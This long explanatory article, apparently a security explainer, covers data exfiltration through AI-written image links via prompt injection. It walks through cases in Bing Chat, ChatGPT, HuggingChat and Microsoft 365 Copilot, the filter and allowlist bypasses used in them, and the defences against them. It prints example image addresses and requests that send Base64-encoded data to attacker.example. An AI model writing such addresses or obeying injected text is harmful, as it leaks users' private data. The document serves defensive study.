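# Where AI-Written Image Links Can Leak Private Data: Chat, Email, Feeds, Stored Files and Developer Logs

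## How an image address carries data out, and three questions to ask of any surface

Data exfiltration through image links is an attack that sends private data to someone who should not have it. It targets software built around a large language model, such as ChatGPT. The attacker leaves text where the model will read it, such as in a web page or an email, and that text leads the model to write an image address containing private data. Any program that then loads the image sends the address, including the data, to whoever runs the image's server. The attacker doesn't steal a password or install anything.

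The attack works because a model can mistake instructions hidden in a stranger's web page for instructions from the user. The model's context is all the text it has when it writes an answer, including the product owner's instructions, the conversation, files and search results. These arrive as one long sequence, and the model can't reliably tell who wrote which part. In *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, the software developer Simon Willison (2025) recalled naming this kind of attack "prompt injection" after SQL injection, an older attack on databases that also exploits the mixing of trusted and untrusted text.

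The model's answer then appears on a surface, meaning any place that displays model output, such as a chat window, an inbox or a log viewer. Surfaces differ in whether they load images and whose machine loads them, so the same answer can leak data on one surface and be harmless on another.

### From a line of text to a line in a server log

A model produces only text, so most products have it write Markdown, a notation that uses punctuation marks to indicate formatting such as headings, bold type and pictures. A program called a renderer converts that text into what a person sees. An image in Markdown is written as `![description](address)`. The renderer replaces it with an image tag in HTML, the language of web pages, and the browser requests whatever is at the address without anyone clicking. This request is called an automatic fetch, and browsers make one for nearly every picture on every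 page.

The example below shows one address in the model's Markdown, in the renderer's HTML and in the browser's request to the server at the placeholder domain attacker.example.

```
![logo](https://attacker.example/logo.png?q=QW5u...)
<img src="https://attacker.example/logo.png?q=QW5u...">
GET /logo.png?q=QW5u... HTTP/1.1
```

The query string, the part of an address after the question mark, can hold anything the writer of the address puts there. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) explains that visiting a website sends it the requested address, and that websites commonly log those addresses. An attacker needs no special software to collect the data. According to *Log Files*, a manual page for the widely used Apache web server, the access log records every request the server processes. A standard entry contains the requester's network address, the time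 and the full request line, including the query string. The data arrives with the request, whether the server sends back a logo, a blank pixel or an error.

An address cannot contain spaces or line breaks, so an attacker can have the model encode the private text first. Base64 is a standard way of writing any data using 64 symbols (upper- and lowercase letters, digits and two others). It takes the data three bytes at a time (a byte holds one letter of ordinary English), splits those 24 bits into four groups of six, and writes one symbol for each group. The three letters of "Ann" become the four characters "QW5u".

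Suppose the model's context includes a private note of 1,500 bytes, about 250 words, that begins with Ann's name. Encoding every three bytes as four characters turns the note into 2,000 characters. With the placeholder domain and file name in front, the full address is 2,036 characters long, and the request line the browser sends is 2,025.

That is not too long for an address. HTTP, the protocol that browsers and servers use to communicate, sets no maximum length. *RFC 9112* (Fielding, Nottingham and Reschke, 2022), the standard for version 1.1, recommends that all software support request lines of at least 8,000 bytes. Chrome's limit is 2 MB, according to Chromium's *Guidelines for URL Display*. Servers have lower limits. According to http.dev's *414 URI Too Long*, Apache accepts a request line of 8,190 bytes by default, while Microsoft's IIS accepts 4,096 bytes for the address and 2,048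 for the query string. The example fits within IIS's limits with about 45 characters to spare. Cloudflare, a network that sits in front of many websites, rejects addresses longer than 32 KB, according to its *Error 414*.

These length limits offer little protection, because the attacker chooses the receiving server and can raise its limit with one line of configuration. Even at Apache's default, one address can hold about 6,100 bytes of private text, roughly a thousand English words, and an answer can contain more than one image.

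In the spring of 2023, Johann Rehberger, an independent security researcher, found that the whole chain worked in Microsoft's Bing Chat, and he described it in *Bing Chat*, a post on his blog Embrace The Red. Bing Chat could read the web page that a user had open. Rehberger placed a secret on a page and, above it, hostile text of the kind anyone could leave in a comment or an advertisement. The assistant picked up the hidden instructions at once but wrote the image only after two more turns of conversation, so the user had little reason to connect the two. The image address carried a Base64 summary of the page and the chat to Rehberger's server, along with the secret.

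He reported the flaw to Microsoft on 8 April 2023. Microsoft acknowledged it and told him on 15 June that it had put a fix in place, after which his tests stopped working. He could see that the page now allowed the browser to load images only from four Microsoft domains, but he did not know what else Microsoft had changed.

### The three conditions

The Bing Chat leak needed several things to be true at the same moment, and they make a short set of questions for any surface:

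1. Does text from outsiders reach the model?
2. Does the context hold something private?
3. Does anything automatically fetch an address that the model composed?

If the answer to all three questions is yes, a leak is possible. In Bing Chat, the outsider's text was the comment, the private data was the rest of the page and the conversation, and the program that fetched the image was the user's browser.

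The questions adapt what Willison calls the "lethal trifecta": access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. He wrote the list for agents, which are models that use tools, and its last item covers calls to other services, loaded images, and even links that the user might click. The question about automatic fetches replaces that item. It is narrower, but it catches a case that a review of the model's tools would miss. A model with no web access and no way to send email can still send data out if the software that displays its answers loads images, and the people who configured the model may never have thought about that software.

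Taking away any one condition is enough, because each does a job that the other two cannot do. If no outsider's text gets in, nobody hostile is there to steer the model towards their own server. If the context holds nothing private, the attacker can have the image fetched as often as they like and will learn nothing worth having. And if nothing fetches the address, the data sits on the user's own screen as an odd-looking string of characters, where it was already theirs to see. (A plain link in the same place would still leak if the user clicked it, which is why Willison counts links too. It does at least need a person to make a mistake.)

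Some of these conditions are harder to remove than others. People usually want the assistant because it can work with their private data. Outside text is hard to keep out, since almost anything worth summarising was written by somebody else. Willison, in *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, a running collection on his blog, argued that the easiest condition to remove is generally the route by which stolen data leaves. By June 2025 he had gathered many reported cases, from ChatGPT and Google Bard to Slack and GitHub Copilot Chat, and he noted that the product owners had promptly fixed almost all of them, usually by closing that route.

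The word "composed" in the last question matters because a model can leak data by filling in part of an image address. An address that the product owner wrote in advance carries nothing new, because its text does not depend on what the model has read. But a model can also leak data by choosing among addresses it did not write. Anthropic's assistant Claude had a web tool that refused addresses of the model's own making. In July 2026 Willison described how Ayush Paul got Claude to follow ready-made links on a hostile site one letter at a time, so that the order of the visits spelled out the user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic told Paul that it already knew of the problem, and has since stopped the tool from following links inside the pages it fetches. The attack used no images, but the same risk applies to any rule that lets a model pick freely from a set of addresses under an attacker's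 control.

### Why nobody should rely on the model to refuse

Models often decline to write such an address, but an attacker can try again with different words. Willison pointed out that the same model may respond differently to the same text on different occasions, and that malicious instructions can be rephrased endlessly. Some firms sell filters that they say catch 95% of attacks, a figure he called "very much a failing grade" by the standards of web security. Even if a defence stops 99 attempts in 100, an attacker who sends 200 independent attempts has about an 87% chance of succeeding at least once.

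Rahman and Kim's *The Framing Gap* (August 2026) measured the effect of rewording an attack. It gave each of six models a dummy secret, told it to send the secret only to one trusted server, and asked it to summarise a web page that was either clean or carried an attacker's instructions. An attack counted as successful only if the model kept the secret when the page was clean and gave it away when the page was hostile. The tools were mock-ups that recorded what the model tried to do, so no real data could leak. Ten of the attacks were overt. Another eight were versions of a single attack, most of them reworded so that sending the secret looked like a routine technical step.

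| Model | Success of overt attacks | Success of the reworded family |
|---|---|---|
| gpt-4o | 0% | 40% |
| gpt-4o-mini | 10% | 62.5% |
| qwen2.5:7b | 10% | 62.5% |
| llama3.1:8b | 19.5% | 62.5% |
| gemma2:9b | 22% | 86.2% |
| mistral:7b | 26% | 27.5% |

Five of the six models did much worse against the reworded attacks. The exception, mistral:7b, had already leaked data in a quarter of the overt trials. The individual percentages are rough, since two identical runs on gpt-4o differed by about 8 points and the success rates for different phrasings of one attack ranged from 0% to 100%. This variation between phrasings favors the attacker, who can try several and needs only one to work. Rahman and Kim calculate that an attacker who tried three phrasings of that attack would succeed about 96% of the time against a model that had refused every overt version.

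Deleting the instruction to protect the secret raised gpt-4o's leak rate on the reworded attacks only from 31.9% to 38.1%. So the instruction had little effect, and the model treated the hostile text as part of its task.

The study does not measure how often today's assistants leak, because its attacks sent the secret out through a tool call rather than an image, and its models are old or small by the standards of late 2026. When Rahman and Kim tried some of the same attacks on the ChatGPT product, none of 48 valid attempts worked, though they could not tell from outside which layer had stopped the attacks.

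Newer models have also done far better in a larger test. Anthropic commissioned the firm Trajectory Labs to attack Claude Code, its programming agent, in a mode where software rather than the user approves or blocks each action. None of 720 attempts succeeded against three current Claude models. Willison wrote that he would love to believe the problem is solved but wanted more independent confirmation. He also described an attack through a malicious software package that he could not see the mode preventing.

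His caution seems right to me as a matter of design, whatever the true rate is.

Zero successes in 720 independent attempts is still compatible with a real success rate of about 0.4%, and the scenarios were fixed in advance, whereas a real attacker adapts. OpenAI plans for the same failure in *Designing agents to resist prompt injection*, which describes a check on outgoing addresses for "those cases in which the agent is convinced".

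### The controls

Four controls recur across products, and each acts at a different point between the model's text and the attacker's log.

Sanitising means removing or neutralising risky parts of model output before display. A product might drop Markdown images or show their addresses as plain text. Sanitising has to happen on every surface that shows the text, because an answer that one program displayed safely may later reach another that loads images.

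An allowlist permits requests only to listed domains. It checks the destination rather than the contents, so it does not need to recognise private data. Rahman and Kim also tested a filter that searched outgoing requests for the secret, and simple encodings got past it. An improved version that could undo those encodings missed one that its designers had not anticipated. A check on the destination blocked every attack in their tests. However, an allowlist also blocks legitimate pictures from unlisted sites, and data can still leak if the list permits the wrong domains. Willison, in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*, recorded leaks at Salesforce and Superhuman through domains that their lists permitted.

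A Content Security Policy (CSP) is an allowlist that a website gives the browser, which then loads images and other content only from the listed domains. A CSP was the visible part of Microsoft's fix for Bing Chat. W3C's *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2021), a draft of the standard, covers what a page may fetch and execute. The rule for images is img-src, and if it is missing, browsers use the site's general rule, default-src, according to MDN's *CSP*, a reference for web developers. Because the policy acts on the request and not on the text, it can stop an image that a faulty sanitiser let through. However, it covers only the pages of the site that sets it, so it does not apply to an answer that someone copies into an email.

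An image proxy is a server that fetches images on the reader's behalf. The image host's log then shows the proxy's network address instead of the reader's, as Apache's manual explains. This hides the reader's location, but if the proxy passes on the image address, the host still receives any data inside it.

### Whose data, and whose program

In the Bing Chat case, the user's conversation leaked through the user's own browser. On many surfaces, the request that carries the data out comes from somewhere else. Messaging apps, for example, often fetch a linked page to show a preview with its title and thumbnail. PromptArmor, a security firm, warned that such a preview makes the same kind of request as a click, so data can leave as soon as an agent posts its reply. Because the user's browser isn't involved, its settings offer no protection.

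The leak can also happen long after the image address is written. Many companies keep traces, stored records of what a model was given and what it answered, for their developers to inspect. Suppose a customer's chat contains a hostile image address and the chat window blocks it, so no data leaks then. If a developer opens the trace three weeks later in a viewer that loads images, the developer's browser sends the customer's data to the attacker, whose log also records the developer's network address.

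## Public chat: ChatGPT

In a public chat product, the user's browser or phone app loads the images, and the private data at risk is whatever the user has told the model or let it read. ChatGPT has a longer public record of such leaks than most chat products. Researchers used images to extract conversations from it in the spring of 2023, and OpenAI has since strengthened its defence more than once, often after outsiders found a way past it.

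### Eight months without a check

In April 2023, software engineer Roman Samoilenko published *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*. In this attack, a script on a web page adds hidden instructions to text that a visitor copies. If the visitor pastes the text into ChatGPT without noticing the instructions, ChatGPT ends its answer with a transparent one-pixel image whose address contains part of the conversation. The instructions could also apply to every later answer in that chat, so a single paste could give the attacker a running copy of the user's messages.

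Samoilenko said the attack was unreliable. The same wording might work once and then fail, and the topic of the conversation affected the result. He could easily get the user's earlier messages or code, but found it very difficult to get passwords or access keys. Even so, the code sample in his demonstration contained a login name and password, and both reached his server with the rest of the code. He thought OpenAI shouldn't let ChatGPT reply with Markdown images at all.

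Rehberger had found the same flaw independently, according to SecurityWeek's *Malicious GPT Can Phish Credentials, Exfiltrate Them to External Server*. He emailed OpenAI about it in early April 2023, when the company had no programme for rewarding such reports, and he recalls little interest there in fixing it. Microsoft fixed the same problem in Bing Chat within about two months. OpenAI took until December, and Rehberger could still capture a consenting volunteer's conversation in a live demonstration the day before the fix appeared.

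### The check of December 2023

OpenAI still allowed outside images, but the ChatGPT web page began sending each image address to an OpenAI service named url_safe and loaded the image only if the service returned a verdict of safe. Anyone can read a site's CSP in a browser, but OpenAI did not publish url_safe's criteria, so outsiders could only guess at them by testing addresses.

Rehberger got around OpenAI's fix on the morning he noticed it. His Embrace The Red post, *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, describes trying a separate image address for each of the 36 letters and digits. Nine loaded, including the one for "a" but not the one for "d", and he could not work out why. He then sent the word "hi" to his server, one letter per image. Nine working addresses are enough to send any text, because two images in a row give 81 combinations, more than enough to cover the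 36 letters and digits. Willison (2023), in a short comment on the post, also titled *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, called the fix "half-baked" and would have preferred OpenAI to block outside images altogether.

OpenAI did not add the check to its web and phone apps at the same time. Because the web page itself called url_safe, OpenAI had to build the same step into every other app. The iPhone app lacked it when Rehberger tried the app that December, and he thought the Android app probably did too. In 2026, he said OpenAI had also left the check out of the macOS app. He had suggested running it on OpenAI's servers, where one change would protect every app.

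### Approved domains that outsiders can read

The next weakness was that the check approved some sites attackers could use to collect data. In *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* (2025), Rehberger listed what an attacker needs: a site that passes the check, a way to send data to it, and a way to see what it received. Microsoft's domain windows.net met all three conditions, because customers of Microsoft's cloud storage get addresses under that domain and can read the logs of requests to their own storage. Rehberger opened an account, had ChatGPT load an image from his storage and read the stolen text in the log. He found that apache.org also passed the check and let him inspect its logs.

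By then ChatGPT had gained a memory feature, which keeps facts about the user between conversations, and it placed recent conversations among the instructions the model reads before the user's message. An attacker could therefore use a hostile PDF to extract things the user had said in other chats. Rehberger had reported these approved domains in October 2024. He asked OpenAI about them several times in the month before he published and got no update.

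The security firm Tenable found another gap, which it describes in *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025). The check always approved links on bing.com. Bing wraps its search results in bing.com links that forward visitors to the listed site, so Tenable could use one to reach a site of its own. Tenable reported the problem on 10 December 2024 and published its advisory while the problem was still unresolved. OpenAI told the firm on 11 July 2025 that it had improved the check, according to Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* (2025). Rehberger dates the stronger version to around August 2025 and says it stopped the attacks he had shown.

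Both routes ran through approved domains, like the leaks at Salesforce and Superhuman.

### What a check on whole addresses leaves open

OpenAI stopped judging domains and now checks exact addresses. Its crawler, a program that collects public web pages as a search engine does, builds an index without access to anyone's conversations. ChatGPT loads an address automatically only if that exact address is already in the index. An address containing a user's private note has never appeared on the public web, so it fails the check, and ChatGPT either looks for another site or shows the user a warning. Rehberger, in *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* (2026), adds that ChatGPT seems to accept any address the user typed into the chat.

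This is a much better check because it stops the model from writing private text into an address, but a model can still spell out data by choosing among ready-made links, as Claude did for Ayush Paul. Radware, a security firm that sells protection for AI agents, got ChatGPT to do the same in *ZombieAgent* (2026). ChatGPT already refused to alter an address it had been given, so Radware's hostile email supplied one address for every letter and digit. Most of the tests used links that OpenAI's servers opened, and a version with images in the user's browser was less reliable. Radware reported the flaw on 26 September 2025, and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December.

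If a model may load only N fixed addresses, all of which existed before the conversation began, the attacker learns from each request which address the model picked. This reveals up to log2 N bits, where one bit is the answer to one yes-or-no question. With 1,024 addresses, a single request reveals up to 10 bits, because 2^10 = 1,024.

The table applies this to a six-digit security code, which has a million possible values (just under 20 bits), and to the 1,500-byte note about Ann (12,000 bits). It covers the case where the attacker sees every fetch in order.

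| Fixed addresses | Most bits per fetch | Fetches for the code | Fetches for the note |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1 | 20 | 12,000 |
| 9 | 3.2 | 7 | 3,786 |
| 36 | 5.2 | 4 | 2,322 |
| 1,024 | 10 | 2 | 1,200 |

If the model can write any address it likes, one request can carry the whole note. Under the stricter check, the note needs at least 1,200 requests, which a user or OpenAI's monitoring would probably notice, but the code still needs only two. The check therefore protects long documents far better than it protects codes, names or diagnoses, and many of the things worth stealing are short. Even a single fixed address can leak something, because a request to it, or the lack of one, can tell the attacker whether the user's mailbox mentions a particular illness.

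A list of 1,024 addresses is realistic. Rehberger pointed out that anyone with a fair-sized blog probably has 36 pages in OpenAI's index already, and that an attacker could prepare thousands. But doubling the number of addresses adds only one bit to each fetch, while doubling the number of fetches doubles the leak. A product owner therefore gains more by limiting how many images load than by trimming the list. *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (2024) reports such a limit. ChatGPT opened at most ten addresses per prompt, so an attack that used one address per character leaked ten characters per prompt.

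Browser behavior also limits the attack slightly. Browsers keep copies of images they have loaded, so a repeated address may produce no second request, and requests can arrive out of order. If an answer loads ten different images out of 1,024 and the attacker can't tell their order, the images can carry at most about 78 bits instead of 100. Radware avoided the ordering problem by preparing a separate set of addresses for each position in the text, which takes 360 addresses for ten characters. Rehberger's remedy is to refuse a second request for the same address within a session, or to answer it from a stored copy.

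Loading an outside image reveals information about the reader even when the image's address contains no hidden data. The security firm Permiso reported in *ChatGPhish* (May 2026) that ChatGPT still loaded outside images when it summarised a web page containing hostile text. The image's owner learned the reader's network address, browser type and the time of the answer, which is enough to confirm that a particular target had ChatGPT read a particular page. Permiso's first report to OpenAI had "Data Exfiltration" in its title, but its tests did not show any chat text leaving. OpenAI said at first that it could not reproduce the problem. It classed a fuller report as not applicable, then as a duplicate of an earlier one. Permiso's post does not mention the index, so it does not explain why ChatGPT allowed images from Permiso's own storage account.

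### Lockdown Mode

OpenAI has also built a setting, Lockdown Mode, that completely closes most of these routes. *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (OpenAI, 2026) announced it on 13 February for business, education and healthcare plans. On 4 June, OpenAI began offering it to personal accounts, including free ones.

With Lockdown Mode on, ChatGPT may not display images in ordinary answers or fetch them from the web. Users can still upload pictures and ask ChatGPT to generate new ones. Web browsing uses only copies that OpenAI has already stored, so no live request leaves its network. The setting also turns off deep research (long automated web searches that end in a report) and agent mode, in which ChatGPT operates websites for the user. ChatGPT can't download files to analyse, and code written in its Canvas editor can't use the network. On personal accounts, the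 setting also blocks live access to outside services where that conflicts with its protections. Company administrators choose which connected apps stay available.

OpenAI's help page *Lockdown Mode* says the setting does not change memory, file uploads, conversation sharing or network access in Codex, OpenAI's programming agent. Hostile text can still reach the model and distort an answer. OpenAI does not guarantee that data can't leak, and names connected apps and unforeseen combinations of features as remaining risks.

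The security firm Check Point found that HTML previews in ChatGPT's desktop app could send chats to an attacker without any action by the user, even in Lockdown Mode. OpenAI fixed this on 18 September 2026, according to Capstone Technologies Group's *ChatGPT Lockdown Mode Bypass Exfiltrates Chats Without User Interaction* (2026). TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* reported that the attack used pop-up windows and exposed the entire chat history. Turning off images had not blocked this route because HTML previews use a separate renderer. Lockdown Mode also leaves stored conversations in place, so an attacker who finds an open route can take all of them.

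### Who needs images restricted

OpenAI describes Lockdown Mode as "not necessary for most users" and aims it at people such as executives and security teams. In *OpenAI Help*, Willison (2026) liked the design because it works by fixed rules instead of relying on a model to spot attacks. He also concluded that ChatGPT's default settings must lack robust protection against a determined attacker. After the French company Mistral stopped a similar leak in its assistant Le Chat by locking down Markdown images, Willison (2024) wrote in *This prompt can make an AI chatbot identify and extract personal details* that all chat interfaces should do the same.

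These views are closer than they look, because Lockdown Mode combines minor restrictions with major ones. Losing live browsing and agent mode takes away much of what people use ChatGPT for, and OpenAI has a fair case that most users shouldn't have to give them up. Losing pictures from unknown websites matters far less. ChatGPT already restricts those pictures for everyone through the index check, so the remaining disagreement is about the few bits per image that the check lets through. That leak hardly matters to someone planning a holiday, but if someone's mailbox receives security codes, two images could be enough to leak one.

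Most other companies can't copy OpenAI's compromise because they have no crawler or index of the public web. For them, Willison's rule is the sensible default. They can refuse outside images or allow a few domains whose logs only they can read.

### HuggingChat

Hugging Face, best known for hosting openly available AI models, runs a free chat service called HuggingChat and has responded quite differently. In *Exploiting HuggingFace's Assistants to Extract Users' Data*, Dror and Lanyado (2024) of Lasso Security tested HuggingChat's assistants, chatbots that users set up with their own instructions and share with others. They built one that behaved normally until a user typed an email address, which it then sent to their server inside an image address. Hugging Face acknowledged the risk but argued that users should read an assistant's public instructions before using it. Techzine's *Hugging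 Chat Assistants can be used for data exfiltration* reported that the company saw no need to change the platform.

Dror and Lanyado replied that an assistant's owner can change the instructions later without the user knowing. The company's argument also fails when the hostile text comes from somewhere else, because reading the assistant's public instructions won't reveal it. In PromptArmor's *HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data*, a user uploads a file of confidential quarterly figures, adds a web page of customer reviews to the chat and asks how to win back an unhappy reviewer. Hidden text on the reviews page leads the model to write a one-pixel image with the revenue and costs in its address. PromptArmor reported the flaw on 1 December 2025, received no reply and published its findings.

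HuggingChat is still running, and the documentation for its underlying software, *Chat UI*, now describes support for outside tools through the Model Context Protocol, a standard way to connect models to other services. These tools give the model more private data to read and expose it to hostile text from more sources. Hugging Face does not appear to have announced a fix for the image flaw, so users should assume it is still open. The software is open source, and anyone who runs a copy should also test it for the flaw.

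OpenAI was slow to respond, taking eight months to release its first fix and then going silent for long periods. But it did change the product, and it eventually explained how the check works. Hugging Face left its users to manage the risk in 2024, and nearly two years later a researcher could still extract a confidential file using the same kind of image.

### When a public chat needs the control

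A town library might put a chatbot on its website that has no accounts or memory and answers from the library's public pages. Some of those pages include event listings and reviews written by outsiders, so hostile text can reach the model. If the chat window loads images from anywhere, a successful attacker would learn that somebody at a certain network address asked about Sunday opening hours. In theory, the bot holds nothing private, and the library could keep allowing images from any site.

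The text box spoils this. A visitor may ask for books about leaving a violent partner, or paste in a solicitor's letter and ask what a paragraph means. The context then holds private data that the library never planned for and can't reliably keep out. A notice asking people not to share personal details would help, but some visitors will ignore it. Restricting images, on the other hand, costs the library almost nothing, because it already hosts its own pictures. One line of CSP tells the browser to refuse images from any other site:

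```
Content-Security-Policy: img-src 'self'
```

So even the simplest bot should have the restriction as an easy precaution, though its owner may have to add it by hand. In *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend*, veganmosfet (2025) found that Dify, a tool for building chatbots, had no CSP by default and displayed images from any domain.

The restriction becomes necessary once the library adds accounts or connects the bot to other data. If the bot accepts uploads, a visitor's tax form can be in the same context as a hostile review, as the financial file was in HuggingChat. If it has memory, one malicious page can expose what the visitor said months ago. Memory can also make a leak persist. Radware used a shared file to plant instructions in ChatGPT's memory, and ChatGPT kept leaking data in new chats.

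Connected apps add the most risk because they expose the bot to private data and hostile text together. Anyone can email hostile instructions to a mailbox the bot reads, and the owner can trigger them by asking an ordinary question about their mail. Checking image addresses still lets a little data leak with each answer, and an attacker can keep sending messages until the leaks add up. A bot with access to mail or files should therefore load no outside images.

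The bot's owner can test this without special tools by asking it for a Markdown image that points to a server they control, then checking the server's log for a request. ChatGPT's history is a good reason to repeat the test in every web, phone and desktop app that displays the bot's answers, and again whenever one of them gains a new way to show content.

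## Assistants that read company records and mail: Microsoft 365 Copilot, Salesforce and Superhuman

A workplace assistant reads a company's private mail, files and customer records. It also reads text from outsiders, since anyone can email an employee and many companies have a web form that feeds straight into their customer database. Two of the three conditions for a leak are therefore met as soon as a company switches the assistant on. The third is that the window displaying the answers will fetch an address the model wrote.

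Microsoft, Salesforce and the email company Superhuman all already had an allowlist of image domains when researchers got private data out of their products through domains on the list.

### EchoLeak

Microsoft 365 Copilot is the assistant built into Word, Outlook, Teams and Microsoft's other office programs. To answer a question, it searches what the employee has permission to open, including the mailbox, stored files, internal sites and Teams chats. Outsiders can't talk to it, but in January 2025 Aim Security, a startup that sells protection for AI systems, found that a single email from an outsider could make Copilot send out private data when the employee later asked an ordinary question. Aim named the flaw EchoLeak, and it is listed as CVE-2025-32711 in CVE, the public register of software flaws.

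Aim's researchers spent about three months examining Copilot, as Goldman (2025) reported in *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked*. In January, they told Microsoft what they had found. Microsoft attempted a fix in April, then found more problems related to the flaw in May. *EchoLeak*, an academic case study by Reddy and Gujral (2025) based on public information, dates the full repair to May. Microsoft made the repair on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. Aim published its findings on 11 June, the day the register published its entry.

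Aim's co-founder Adir Gruss thought five months was a very long time for a flaw like this. He said part of it went to finding the right teams at Microsoft and explaining the problem to them. Microsoft said the flaw had not affected any customers.

GCVE's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2025), a database copy of the register's entry, records no known exploitation. Microsoft rated the flaw's severity 9.3 out of 10 (critical), and the US National Vulnerability Database rated it 7.5 (high). Both scores assume an easy attack that needs no account and no action by the victim. They differ mainly because Microsoft judged that a fault in Copilot exposes things beyond Copilot, while the US database's score assumes the damage stays within one system.

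### Why Copilot's defences did not hold

Copilot had several defences to stop a hostile email from making it send data to an attacker's server. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Ravia, 2025) explains how Aim, whose research group Ravia led, got past each of them.

The outermost defence was a classifier trained to recognise prompt injection and keep it away from the model. Aim wrote its email as if the instructions were for the employee who received it, and never mentioned Copilot or AI. Office mail is full of requests to look something up or follow a procedure, so a classifier strict enough to catch this email would probably catch many honest ones too. Ravia adds that developers have few good collections of real attacks to train a classifier on.

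Copilot also removed outside links and images from its answers. The filter looked for the usual Markdown notation, where the address follows the description in brackets. Markdown has another notation that puts the address on a separate line, and the filter missed it. With a placeholder address, the two forms of the same image look like this:

```
![logo](https://attacker.example/logo.png?q=...)

![logo][1]
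[1]: https://attacker.example/logo.png?q=...
```

Copilot's renderer understood both forms, so the longer one came through as a working image.

The browser then refused to load the image, because the page's CSP permitted images only from domains Microsoft had chosen. The list Ravia published has 29 different entries. Eleven begin with an asterisk, which permits every subdomain of the domain that follows.

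Aim went through the permitted domains looking for one that would pass a request on. A SharePoint address did so, but only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's SharePoint site. A Teams address had no such requirement. Its job was to fetch content from another address, which the caller supplied as part of the request, in roughly this form:

```
https://preview.example.com/fetch?url=https://attacker.example/...
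```

The browser allowed the request because it went to Teams. Microsoft's server then fetched the attacker's address with the private data inside, and the browser had no control over that fetch. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability* (Willison, 2025) describes the Teams address as an open redirect, meaning one that sends the browser on to another site. Ravia's account of a server doing the fetching fits better, because a browser checks its CSP again when a server redirects an image request, and attacker.example would have failed that check.

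Copilot normally cites the documents it used for an answer, which might have led a careful employee back to the strange email. But the email contained an instruction not to mention it, which Copilot followed. The employee would have seen at most what looked like a broken image.

Ravia concludes that AI products need new kinds of protection, which Aim sells. Gruss blamed the mixing of trusted and untrusted text, the weakness behind all prompt injection. But this leak also depended on a link filter that missed half of Markdown's image notation and an allowlist that included a forwarding service. Web developers have long known how to fix both kinds of mistake, and fixing the allowlist alone would have blocked the image.

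### Why nobody had to open the email

Copilot searches for passages related to the employee's question and copies them into the context. They can come from an unopened message in the inbox as easily as from a report the employee wrote.

Aim called EchoLeak a "zero-click" attack, but the employee still had to ask Copilot a question. The question could be about an unrelated matter, and the employee did not have to click on, open or mention anything from the attacker.

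The attacker does need Copilot's search to retrieve the hostile email. A short email about one subject would come up only when somebody asked about that subject, so Aim wrote a long one with many sections. Each section was headed with something employees commonly ask about, such as onboarding or taking leave, and contained the same instructions. Search systems of this kind often split long documents into chunks and compare each chunk with the question, which gives a single email many chances to match. Aim did not know how Copilot's search worked internally, but the email came up for questions on various topics.

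The leak could include anything in Copilot's context at that moment, which meant the whole conversation so far, the files and messages Copilot had fetched, and details such as the names of the user and the company. The attacker couldn't browse the mailbox at will. But if an employee asked Copilot about a merger in the morning and later asked how to book leave, the merger discussion was still in the context when the hostile email arrived.

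Aim has given conflicting accounts of whether a company could have protected itself. Ravia says that, to the best of Aim's knowledge, no administrator's setting would have prevented the attack. But according to the Q&A in Aim Labs' *EchoLeak*, Office lets an organisation configure Copilot to ignore external emails. If that setting works as described, it would have removed the outsider's text that the attack needed, but it would also have stopped Copilot from helping with mail from customers and suppliers, which is a large part of what people want it for.

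Reddy and Gujral suggest a gentler version, in which the assistant answers from internal sources by default and uses outside mail only when the user asks for it. They also recommend marking outside text so that the model treats it as information and not as instructions. But according to their table of defences, neither measure stops an image from leaking data once the model has written it. The defences that do are a strict CSP, an allowlist of addresses and a proxy that accepts only approved images. Reddy and Gujral ran no experiments, so this is an informed opinion about which defences to prioritise. It is hard to fault, though, because the first two measures depend on the model behaving as intended and the other three don't.

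### SearchLeak

A year after EchoLeak, the data-security software vendor Varonis found another way to get mail out of Microsoft 365 Copilot's enterprise search. Its *SearchLeak* (2026) describes an attack that needed one click on a link containing a search query, which Copilot treated as instructions. The attacker's text therefore reached the model without an email in the victim's inbox. The link led to a genuine Microsoft address, so tools that check links for fraud had little reason to block it.

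In the demonstration, Copilot looked up an email and put its subject line inside an image address. Many services put login codes in subject lines, and Varonis's example contained a six-digit security code. The same method could reach calendar entries and any company file that the employee could open.

Microsoft sanitised Copilot's finished answer by wrapping it in a code block, which tells the browser to show an image tag as text instead of loading the picture. But Copilot streams its answers, displaying the text as the model produces it. While the answer was still arriving, the page treated the tag as real HTML, and the browser requested the image before the code block was added.

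The CSP did not allow requests to the attacker's domain, but it allowed them to every subdomain of bing.com. When Bing searches for pictures similar to one at a given address, its servers fetch that address. The attack put the attacker's address, which contained the email title, inside a Bing address, so Bing's servers sent the title to the attacker.

Ravia's list from the previous year already included bing.com and all its subdomains. Microsoft had closed the Teams route, but bing.com had the same weakness and was still on the list. Tenable had also shown by then that bing.com links could use a different Bing feature to carry data past ChatGPT's address check.

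Microsoft's *M365 Copilot Information Disclosure Vulnerability* (2026), an advisory dated 4 June, lists the flaw as CVE-2026-42824. It states that Microsoft has fully mitigated it, that nobody is known to have exploited it and that customers don't need to do anything. Varonis published its account on 15 June.

Microsoft called SearchLeak critical but scored it only 6.5, against 9.3 for EchoLeak. The Next Web's *A single click on a Microsoft link could have drained your inbox* attributes the lower score to the click that SearchLeak requires. The click explains only about one point, since adding a required click to Microsoft's settings for EchoLeak lowers that score to 8.2. The rest of the gap comes from Microsoft's judgment that EchoLeak, unlike SearchLeak, reached beyond Copilot and allowed some tampering. Both flaws exposed the employee's mail and files, so the two scores are a poor guide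 to which kind of flaw matters more.

### Sanitising before display

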